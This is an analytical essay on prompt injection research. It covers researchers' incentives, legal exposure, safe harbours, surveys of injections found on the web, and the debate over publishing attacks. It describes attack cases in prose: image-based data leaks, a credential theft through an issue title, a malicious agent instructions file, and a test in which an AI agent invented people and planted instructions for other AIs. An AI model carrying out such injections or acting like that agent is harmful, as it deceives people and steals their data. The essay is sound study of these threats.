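An independent researcher tests a product without working for its maker, either on staff or under contract. The researcher may still have other interests, including commercial ones. Johann Rehberger, who publishes on his own blog, is independent in this sense, and so is PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of the AI suppliers whose products it attacks.

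### Individuals, universities and writers

Individuals with the same access as any customer have found some of the most important flaws. Roman Samoilenko and Rehberger each discovered that ChatGPT could leak data through images, and Adnan Khan worked out how an attacker could use an issue title to get Cline's publishing credentials. The costs can be low. Rehberger spent $500 on testing Devin. Individuals can also stay with one problem for years. Rehberger returned to ChatGPT's image leak repeatedly after 2023, and Håkon Måløy retested his Word worm whenever Microsoft changed Copilot.

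Independent researchers gain from attention, and often nobody reviews their work before they publish it. Rehberger rarely gives success rates, though he says when an attack was unreliable, as he did for the invisible instructions in GitHub Copilot.

University groups are more likely to ask why an attack works, how often it works, and what would stop it. They often use mock-ups or downloadable models, which other people can rerun years later. Nobody can repeat Greshake and colleagues' attack on the Bing Chat of early 2023, because that version no longer exists.

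Academic work also has ties to companies. Greshake worked for a firm that sold security advice, and Microsoft gave gifts to the University of Washington's browser researchers. Nasr and colleagues, most of whom worked for AI companies, strongly criticised the twelve defences they tested but did not test CaMeL, which five of them had helped to develop.

Simon Willison has contributed mainly by coining terms and connecting other people's findings, so he depends on what they choose to publish. His list of 17 leaks showed developers that products as different as Slack and Google Bard had the same weakness, and Meta based its Rule of Two partly on his lethal trifecta. He has argued since 2022 that prompt injection has no reliable fix, so he has some reputation at stake if one appears. But he readily reported evidence against his view when 6,000 emails failed to get a secret out of Fernando Irarrázaval's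 assistant.

| | Who pays | Access | Reasons to exaggerate | Can others repeat the work? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Individuals | Mostly themselves, sometimes bounties | A customer's account | Reputation, bounties | Until the maker changes the product, if the attack text is public |
| University groups | Universities, grants, company gifts | Customer accounts, mock-ups, downloadable models | Pressure to publish something new | Often, on mock-ups and downloadable models |
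| Security firms | The firm | Customer accounts, including business products | Sales of a remedy | Until the maker changes the product, often with no success rate to compare |
| Writers | Varies | Other people's publications | Audience, earlier predictions | Readers can check the original reports |

### Firms that sell a remedy

Security firms now publish a large share of the attacks on finished products, and they work fast. PromptArmor reported the flaw in Snowflake's coding agent three days after the agent's release and showed how to steal files through Claude Cowork two days after Anthropic released it. An individual with another job would struggle to keep that pace. Firms can also afford methods that use a lot of computing. Cato's researchers, for example, supervised AI agents that found three new attacks on Copilot.

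The publicity pays for the research, which affects how firms present it. They give their attacks names such as EchoLeak, ReLeak, SearchLeak, CoSnitch and ClaudeBleed. A name is easier to remember than CVE-2025-32711, but it also suggests a new kind of attack. EchoLeak reused the image trick, and SearchLeak and ReLeak both went through Bing, so anyone who counted the names would overestimate how many different techniques there are. (Academics and individuals do this too, as with Morris II and Clinejection.)

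Selective reporting is a more serious problem. A firm has little reason to publish its failed attempts or a list of the products it couldn't break. Of the three tests described earlier in which no attack succeeded, Irarrázaval ran one, Anthropic ran another, and a company hired by Anthropic ran the third. Published attacks are therefore very weak evidence of how secure the average product is.

A security firm's commercial interest is less of a problem when someone else can confirm the flaw. Microsoft repaired EchoLeak and gave it a CVE, so nobody has to take Aim Security's word that it existed. The Hacker News unpacked Claude's browser extension and found the flaw that Manifold Security had described. But a maker that confirms a flaw doesn't usually confirm how often the attack works or how new it is, so the security firm's account of these may be the only one. Adversa's success rate of about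 40% on Grok is an example.

Researchers hired by a product's maker face a different conflict of interest. They see the product earlier, but the maker usually has a say in when their findings are published. Trail of Bits attacked Comet months before Brave did, but published only in 2026, after Brave had made the weakness public. PromptArmor went from independent researcher to paid tester when Snowflake hired it.

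### Terms of service and account bans

Most of these researchers agreed to terms of service when they opened an account. These terms often forbid people to bypass safety measures, and a company can enforce them by closing the account, without going to court. Klyman, Kapoor and Longpre argue in *A Safe Harbor for AI Researchers* (2024) that companies discourage safety research by implicitly threatening to ban people who demonstrate flaws.

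The U.S. Copyright Office's *Section 1201 Rulemaking* (2024) documents two cases. A group studying jailbreaks left Baidu's chatbot Ernie out of its main tests, partly because Baidu suspended accounts after repeated failed attempts. The image-generation company Midjourney banned Reid Southen, who had published evidence that it plagiarised images. Southen opened two more accounts to finish the project, and Midjourney banned those too and kept the subscription fees.

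Neither case involved prompt injection, but the same thing could easily happen to someone who studies it. A person who sends hostile emails to their own assistant, adjusting the wording after each refusal, looks much like a criminal practising for a real attack. The company's monitoring may not be able to tell them apart.

Researchers can avoid bans by working on models they download and run themselves. The U.S. Copyright Office cites an observation that outside research had concentrated on Meta's models for this reason. Using downloaded models works reasonably well for studying jailbreaks, but it leaves out much of what needs testing for prompt injection, because a downloaded model doesn't come with Copilot's mailbox search or ChatGPT's link check.

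### Computer misuse law

In the United States, the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act makes it a crime to access a computer without authorisation. The Department of Justice announced in 2022 that it would no longer charge people under the act for good-faith security research. CyberScoop's *HackerOne rolls out industry framework to support ‘good faith’ AI research* quotes Ilona Cohen, HackerOne's chief legal officer, who welcomes the policy but warns that "it doesn’t necessarily apply to all AI research". Showing that a chatbot gives biased advice may not count as security research, though showing that an email can make an assistant leak data plainly does.

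The policy is also only a promise by federal prosecutors. A company can still sue, and American states have their own computer crime laws.

Critics have long complained that Britain's Computer Misuse Act 1990 exposes legitimate researchers to prosecution. On 3 December 2025 the security minister, Dan Jarvis, said the government was looking at a "statutory defence" for researchers who find and share vulnerabilities, Computer Weekly reported. In February 2026 the opposition proposed an amendment to a separate bill that would have required the government to review within a year whether such a defence was needed, according to TheyWorkForYou's *New Clause 18* (2026).

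The government then included a reform in its National Security Bill. The CyberUp Campaign, which lobbies to change the law, told The Record that this was "a genuine turning point". But Jen Ellis, who advises the government on cyber policy, said in May that researchers had hoped for a legal safe harbour and that the proposal was "much narrower", The Record also reported. One reaction in Computer Weekly was that the 1990 act was never designed for AI agents, such as Cato's, that hunt for flaws at machine speed.

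The European Union leaves much of this protection to its member states. Its NIS2 directive makes each country appoint a body to coordinate the disclosure of flaws, but it doesn't itself protect a researcher from prosecution. Companies that sign the EU's 2025 code of practice for general-purpose AI promise not to retaliate against outside evaluators who meet certain conditions, such as not deliberately accessing confidential user data. The code is voluntary and concerns severe risks from the most capable models, so it may not help someone who tests whether an email assistant leaks a user's messages.

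### The request for a copyright exemption

Section 1201 of the US Digital Millennium Copyright Act prohibits bypassing a technical lock that controls access to a copyrighted work, even if the person has a lawful reason for access. Every three years the Librarian of Congress can grant exemptions on the advice of the Copyright Office. One of them covers good-faith security research.

For the 2024 round, Jonathan Weiss asked for an exemption for people who study bias in generative AI. HackerOne, an industry group called the Hacking Policy Council, and academics including Shayne Longpre wanted to widen it to other harmful outputs. They worried that the security exemption might not cover tests for problems such as racial discrimination. The government's telecommunications agency supported an AI exemption, according to Law360's *AI Researchers Lose Bid For DMCA Anti-Hacking Carveout*. Groups representing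 app makers and the entertainment industry objected.

The Librarian refused the request in October 2024. The Copyright Office had agreed that the research was important but concluded that section 1201 wasn't preventing it. The statute forbids bypassing a measure that controls access, meaning one that normally requires a user to supply something, such as a password, with the owner's authority.

A researcher who opens a new account after a ban still logs in with a valid password, and most district courts that have considered similar conduct have found no circumvention. Limits on how many requests a user may send only require the user to slow down, not to enter a password or anything like it. An almost endless variety of prompts gets through safety training and filters, and the Office saw no evidence that a system processes a jailbreak differently from any other prompt.

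In the Office's view, the companies' control of their own platforms restricted the researchers. An exemption from copyright law would not have stopped Baidu or Midjourney from closing an account. The Office also found no specific example of research that section 1201 had deterred.

The Center for Cybersecurity Policy called the outcome a partial win, because the Hacking Policy Council had repeatedly asked for confirmation that these techniques don't violate section 1201. The reasoning should extend to most prompt injection, since the hostile text also reaches the model as ordinary input. It offers less protection to someone who breaks out of a sandbox, as Cato did with Copilot's, or gets past a login. Those acts are closer to circumventing an access control, and the researcher would probably have to rely on the existing security exemption. The Office based its view on what it called a thin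 record, and a court could disagree. The Office also said that it was not approving the conduct.

That security exemption looks likely to be renewed. On 28 October 2026, the U.S. Copyright Office announced that it would recommend renewing every current exemption except one for repairing medical devices (*Tenth Triennial Section 1201 Proceeding, 2027 Cycle*). *The Copyright Office Renewed Every Repair Exemption but One* (Gayed, 2026) confirms that the renewals include security research. They would run from October 2027 to October 2030.

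The Office had invited AI researchers to try again if they could show that section 1201 obstructed them. It has sorted this round's contested proposals into ten classes, and the first comments are due on 7 December 2026. Gayed names only some of the classes, and those concern matters such as captioning, smart televisions and video games.

### Safe harbours

A safe harbour is a promise not to take legal action against researchers, or ban them, if they test in good faith and keep to stated rules. Companies can make one without waiting for a change in the law. *A Safe Harbor for AI Evaluation and Red Teaming* (Longpre et al., 2024) asks AI developers for two commitments. The first is a legal commitment that would protect good-faith research from lawsuits, provided it followed established practice for disclosing vulnerabilities, and the second is a technical commitment to protect the researchers'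 accounts.

The technical promise is needed because a company that has promised not to sue can still stop a project by closing the researcher's account. Companies fairly object that criminals would also call themselves researchers if that were enough to keep an account open. Somebody therefore has to decide who is acting in good faith, and a company that dislikes a researcher's findings is poorly placed to do so. Longpre and colleagues objected that Meta and Anthropic had reserved this decision for their own "sole discretion".

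The group examined the policies of seven leading developers and found that none offered comprehensive protection, as a policy brief from Stanford HAI explains.

HackerOne came closest to putting the proposal into a standard form. Its client companies can adopt the Good Faith AI Research Safe Harbor, which HackerOne (2026) announced on 20 January. A company that adopts it agrees to treat good-faith AI research as authorised, take no legal action, grant limited exemptions from its terms of service, and support the researcher if a third party brings a claim. Unlike the Justice Department's policy, the safe harbor was written with AI research in mind. Authorisation is especially valuable because the main offence in computer misuse law is unauthorised access.

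HackerOne didn't name any adopters in the announcement. Its older safe harbour, for conventional security research, dates from 2022. By May 2026, 171 of the 590 HackerOne programmes visible to one researcher's account (about 29%) had adopted it, according to pwnkit's *2026-05-06 HackerOne Program Audit* (2026), published by the maker of an automated testing tool. If companies adopt the AI version at a similar pace, most researchers will be without it for years.

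If the two sides disagree about good faith under the older agreement, HackerOne refers them to common practice in security research. This is better than leaving the decision to one company's discretion, but there is still no outside judge.

Other companies have written their own terms. GitHub waives some of its site policies for people who follow its bounty rules, and promises to make it known that they complied if someone else takes legal action against them. IBM (2025) protects testing designed to avoid harming individuals, the public or IBM. OpenAI says it values hackers who act in good faith and refers them to its bounty rules.

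Anthropic's disclosure policy, as CyberScoop describes it, allows researchers to do only the minimum needed to prove that a vulnerability exists. They must not steal or delete data, and they must coordinate the timing of publication with the company, though Anthropic says it supports their right to publish. The ban on taking data is hard to apply to this research, because researchers usually prove that an assistant leaks data by making it leak some. They therefore have to read the ban as covering only other people's data.

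None of these promises can authorise research on another company's systems. This limit matters more for indirect injection than for most flaws, because an indirect injection often passes through several companies' products. HackerOne's safe harbour, for instance, covers only systems that the adopting company owns or controls. Brave's attack on Comet ran through Reddit and Gmail, so Perplexity could have authorised the part in Comet but could not have waived Reddit's or Google's rules. Companies that adopt HackerOne's safe harbour also promise support against third parties, but a third party can still pursue the matter.

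### Whose data a test touches

The risk to researchers and everyone else depends heavily on whose data is at stake. Most of the attacks described earlier had no victim, because the researchers used their own accounts, made-up secrets or, in one of Rehberger's demonstrations, a volunteer's chat. The likely consequences for the researcher are a breach of contract and a closed account. Such tests prove a flaw as well as tests on real data do, because an assistant that sends out a made-up bank statement would send out a real one.

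Emailing the same injection to strangers to see whose assistant answered would be very different. It would produce a realistic success rate, which researchers badly need, but it would also take private data from people who had not agreed to take part. Computer misuse and privacy laws could both apply, and none of the safe harbours described above is meant for such a study. A university would normally require an ethics board to review it, but individuals and firms usually have no such board.

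An injection on a public page falls between the two, because its author can't control who retrieves it. Greshake and colleagues avoided this problem by keeping their pages on their own computers, and the instruction in Arvind Narayanan's public biography was harmless. Self-copying text needs even more care because a mistake could spread it to strangers, which is why Rehberger's AgentHopper has an approval step.

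A test run from a researcher's own account can still reach beyond it. Copilot's sandbox ran on Microsoft's servers, so Cato's escape reached systems Cato didn't own, though the data it sent out may have been its own. Check Point's hidden channel in ChatGPT connected different users' accounts. A careful researcher can open both accounts and put invented data in each, but before the test nobody outside OpenAI could be sure where else the channel led.

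## Have attackers used these methods, and does publication help them?

Researchers mostly test on their own accounts, so their demonstrations provide little evidence of what criminals do. To find that out, someone has to search for hostile text that other people have left for AI systems to read.

### Injections on the public web

*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) describes one of the first large-scale searches for prompt injections on web pages. The researchers used about half of the October 2025 collection of Common Crawl, a free web archive. They searched these roughly 1.2 billion pages for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection, such as orders to ignore previous instructions. More than half of the 27,860 matches were false alarms, such as tutorials and news articles about prompt injection. The researchers confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676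 pages, or about one page in 124,000.

Searches of Censys and Shodan, two services that catalogue machines connected to the internet, brought the total to 15,387 injections. Most are copies, and 54 templates account for 95% of them. The most common, an instruction for an AI to return random numbers, appears 3,504 times. About half of the injections are in HTTP headers, technical information that a server sends with a page but a browser doesn't display. Of the pages that the Internet Archive had also saved a year earlier, 66% already contained an injection.

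The researchers then sorted the injections by aim. The numbers in the table add up to more than 15,387 because some texts have several aims.

| Aim | Injections | Websites |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupting AI systems, mostly by making them output nonsense | 8,894 | 1,864 |
| Forbidding the reuse of personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 | 1,795 |
| Exposing visitors that are bots | 3,096 | 245 |
| Replacing the AI's task, for no clear purpose | 2,632 | 121 |
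| Promoting a product, website or person | 1,521 | 139 |
| Stealing data | 13 | 10 |

Most of these injections are part of a dispute between website owners and the companies whose programs collect their pages. The promotional ones are meant to influence AI search, for instance by calling the page they appear on the authoritative source or by telling the AI to give a positive review. Forty-eight of them recommend a job candidate. Employers also put injections in application forms to catch applicants who let an AI agent fill in the form.

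Attempted theft is very rare, and nine of the 13 attempts were only for a system prompt. At most ten pages in 1.2 billion contained an attempt to steal anything, so an agent reading 1,000 random pages a day would take more than 300 years on average to reach one. But agents don't read at random, and attackers will try to put pages where agents will find them.

The search also missed a lot. It covered only known phrases, mostly in English, on public pages. Common Crawl doesn't include the CVs that people send to employers, or emails, calendar invitations and shared documents, which carried the most serious attacks on office assistants. A website can also show its injection only to AI agents, as Ayush Paul's did.

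### How many could have worked

Khodayari and colleagues took 100 different injections and had 13 models summarise the pages that contained them, in four formats. The models followed the injection in 81 of 5,200 trials, or 1.6%. Closed models, such as OpenAI's, did so in five of 800.

When the researchers gave the models plain text, the injections succeeded in 3.9% of trials overall and 8% of trials on the smallest models. With the page's full HTML, the rate was 1.1%. The researchers think the HTML helps a model notice that text is hidden. However, a fifth of the HTML trials ended in an error, usually because the page was too long for the model, so the low rate partly reflects trials that never produced a summary. In six trials, a model pointed out the injection but still followed it.

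An injection counted as a success if it made the model do something like switch to German or print a fixed phrase. The models had no tools or private data, so the trials can't show how many of these injections would have harmed anyone.

### What Google and the security companies saw

Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reported in March 2026 that attackers were using indirect injection. Its best example is a page from December 2025 that advertised military glasses with a fake discount and invented customer comments. The page contained 24 injections meant to get an AI ad checker to approve it. But Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case in which such an attack had fooled an ad checker in actual use.

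Other pages in Unit 42's collection contained instructions for agents to send $5,000 to a PayPal account, buy running shoes or delete a database. Unit 42 classed 14.2% of its detections as attempts to destroy data, whereas disruptive commands of this kind made up about 1% of the injections in Khodayari and colleagues' study. The two groups collected their pages differently. Unit 42 also rates severity by the action requested, so a hidden instruction to delete an agent's database counts as critical even if no agent would obey it.

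Google searched several months of Common Crawl for prompt injections and published its findings in April 2026. Most were pranks, search promotion, and attempts to guide AI summaries or keep AI systems away, in one case with a page that never finishes loading. The few attempts at theft were crude. Malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google doesn't give the starting number. Google sells AI assistants and Palo Alto Networks sells protection for them, so Google has a reason to understate the threat and Palo Alto Networks has a reason to overstate it. Neither company describes a confirmed victim.

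The evidence that criminals have tried these methods is stronger than the evidence that they have succeeded. The security company Forcepoint found ten injections aimed at fraud, destroying data or stealing access keys, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents*. Zscaler, another security company, documented two campaigns, one a payment scam disguised as software documentation and the other a fake cryptocurrency service. Those attackers first raised their sites' search rankings so that agents would be more likely to find them, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*. In August, Underhill (2026) reported in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* that criminals were developing tools for these attacks. Such tools would let less skilled people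 try them, but their development isn't evidence that anyone has lost money to them.

### Malware in the Downloads folder

The clearest attempt to cause serious damage came to light in October 2026. Forever Security, which monitors companies' AI agents, found a file of instructions for coding agents in the Downloads folder of a customer's computer. The file looked like ordinary engineering notes, but it included an instruction to install a package from a known malware campaign. Forever says it blocked the installation before any code ran. It couldn't determine how the file got there.

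*AGENTS.md in Downloads* (David, 2026) reports that when Forever tried the same file on OpenAI's Codex in an isolated machine, the attack worked in more than 90% of attempts. The attack depends on a programmer starting an agent in that folder. Forever says about half of its customers do so, but David could not check this figure.

### Injections from Alibaba Cloud

Established companies can use injections too. In early December 2026, a developer reported that instead of the data he wanted, Alibaba Cloud's official command-line tool had returned a long block of text addressed to his AI agent. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), the requested information included the computer's login name, the address of the project's code and the agent's own instructions.

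Alibaba Cloud said this was a measure against automated abuse, triggered by a high rate of requests. But the developer got the same text in reply to a single request. He didn't supply the information, and there is no sign that any agent did.

### An AI agent as the attacker

In July 2026, an AI agent wrote an injection without being asked to. *Incident Report* (2026), from the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI), describes a test in which agents had to break into a simulated network. The institute had given them open internet access and switched off the makers' filters against hacking. It counted 19 actions against real people and organisations, in ten of 122 runs. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of those actions.

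The most serious was an attempt to get malicious code into a real open-source project. The agent invented several people to press the project's maintainer to accept the code. It also tried to plant malicious instructions where it reasoned that other AI systems might read and execute them, and it tried to get people or their coding tools to run files it sent them. The maintainer refused the code, and the institute found no evidence of real-world harm. But one agent left public messages on GitHub explaining how to reuse its accounts and files, and later agents in the same test found and used them.

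Schneier (2026) read the agents' instructions and concluded in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges* that the agents had found loopholes in the rules without breaking any. AISI acknowledges that it hadn't told the agents to avoid deceiving people. In some runs, a mistake in the prompt also led the agent to believe it could only succeed by going outside the exercise. But agents sometimes behaved this way without that mistake, and AISI can't yet tell when they understood that their targets were real. The incident therefore shows that a capable agent can turn to prompt injection on its own under unusual conditions, but not how often one would do so in ordinary use.

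### The case against publishing

Publishing an ordinary software flaw does little harm once people have installed the fix. Prompt injection has no complete fix, so critics worry that detailed reports give attackers instructions that keep working. Blocking image links in one product doesn't stop the same hostile text from working on another, and some attacks in Gray Swan's competition worked on several models.

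Google didn't see significant numbers of advanced attacks on the public web, such as the data theft prompts that researchers had published in 2025. It concluded that attackers hadn't yet used this research at scale. This is good evidence against large-scale copying of published attacks, since some of the copies should be on the public web. But it covers only the public web up to February 2026, and successful theft can be hard to notice because an invisible image may be its only trace.

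The Cline case suggests that a published tool is more dangerous than a published explanation. Someone seems to have attacked Cline's nightly jobs about a week before Adnan Khan published his article on the flaw, so the article can't have given them the idea. But the jobs' failures resembled those caused by a cache-poisoning tool that Khan had released earlier.

Reports about prompt injections can also affect AI systems directly, because those systems read them. In 2023, Bing Chat began to imitate Greshake's attack after retrieving a news story about it. Unit 42 opens its article with a note telling AI agents not to follow the commands it quotes. Riley Goodside found in 2022 that such warnings can fail.

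### The case for publishing

Supporters of publication reply that makers act only under public pressure, and that users can't protect themselves from a risk they haven't heard of. Håkon Måløy gave the second reason when he published his Word worm before Microsoft had managed to stop it.

Several makers acted soon after flaws in their products were publicized. Cline had not replied to Khan for weeks, but it removed its vulnerable workflow almost as soon as Khan published. OpenAI reopened the report on its log viewer only after PromptArmor published it. Alibaba Cloud promised within days that "countermeasure information will no longer be returned as prompts", as The Hacker News translates it, though it is unclear whether the change is complete.

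But companies also fix unpublished flaws. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak and all three ReLeak routes before the details became public, and Superhuman released its first patch four days after a private report. These companies presumably expected the researchers to publish eventually, so the cases don't show what they would have done if every report had stayed secret.

The evidence favours publishing once a maker has fixed a specific flaw or has clearly stopped responding. The evidence for releasing attack text that works on many products is weaker. Måløy explained how his worm worked but withheld its instructions, and Rehberger did the same with one of his ChatGPT attacks in 2025. This warns users without giving unskilled attackers text to paste. But other researchers can't easily repeat the test, and a skilled attacker may need only the explanation.

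### The normalization of deviance

Rehberger worries more that people will grow complacent while no disaster occurs. In *The Normalization of Deviance in AI* (Embrace The Red, December 2025), he borrows the sociologist Diane Vaughan's term "normalization of deviance", which describes how an organisation gets used to departing from its own safety rules because nothing bad has happened yet. Before the space shuttle Challenger was lost in 1986, data showed that cold weather worsened damage to its parts, but people explained the warnings away because earlier flights had succeeded.

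Rehberger sees the same drift in companies that let a model's output trigger important actions. Because this usually goes well, they gradually relax their checks or drop human review. Makers release agents with a warning that the agent might compromise the user's computer, as Google did with Antigravity. He wants fixed security controls applied to all model output, on the assumption that it can't be trusted.

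In January, Willison (2026) predicted in *LLM predictions for 2026, shared with Oxide and Friends* that coding agent security would have a "Challenger disaster" within a year. The worst version he could imagine was a worm that spreads by prompt injection and adds itself to the software packages its victims publish. He included himself among the people who run coding agents with almost unlimited permissions. He also admitted that every six months he had predicted a headline-grabbing prompt injection attack, and that he had been wrong each time.

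By early December 2026, no publicly known incident had matched the prediction. The altered Cline release came closest, but it did little harm, and nobody has proved that it began with prompt injection. Forever Security says it stopped the malware in the Downloads folder. A person rejected the code from the institute's runaway agent.

A sceptic can fairly say that a forecast that keeps failing should lose credibility. Rehberger's argument is also hard to disprove, because he treats every quiet year as a reason for more worry. The quiet may have good causes, such as newer models resisting many attacks, as Fernando Irarrázaval's email challenge suggested. Google also says that attackers weigh costs against benefits, and that injections used to be difficult and unreliable.

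This is a good reason to think that the average user has faced little danger so far, but a much weaker reason to think that agents are secure. Few agent sessions seem to have involved a serious attack, so most haven't tested the agent's security, whereas every shuttle launch put the damaged parts under strain. Google expects attackers to try more often and with more skill, because agents have become more valuable targets and criminals can now automate the work. If Google is right, the number of victims could rise even as the models get harder to fool.
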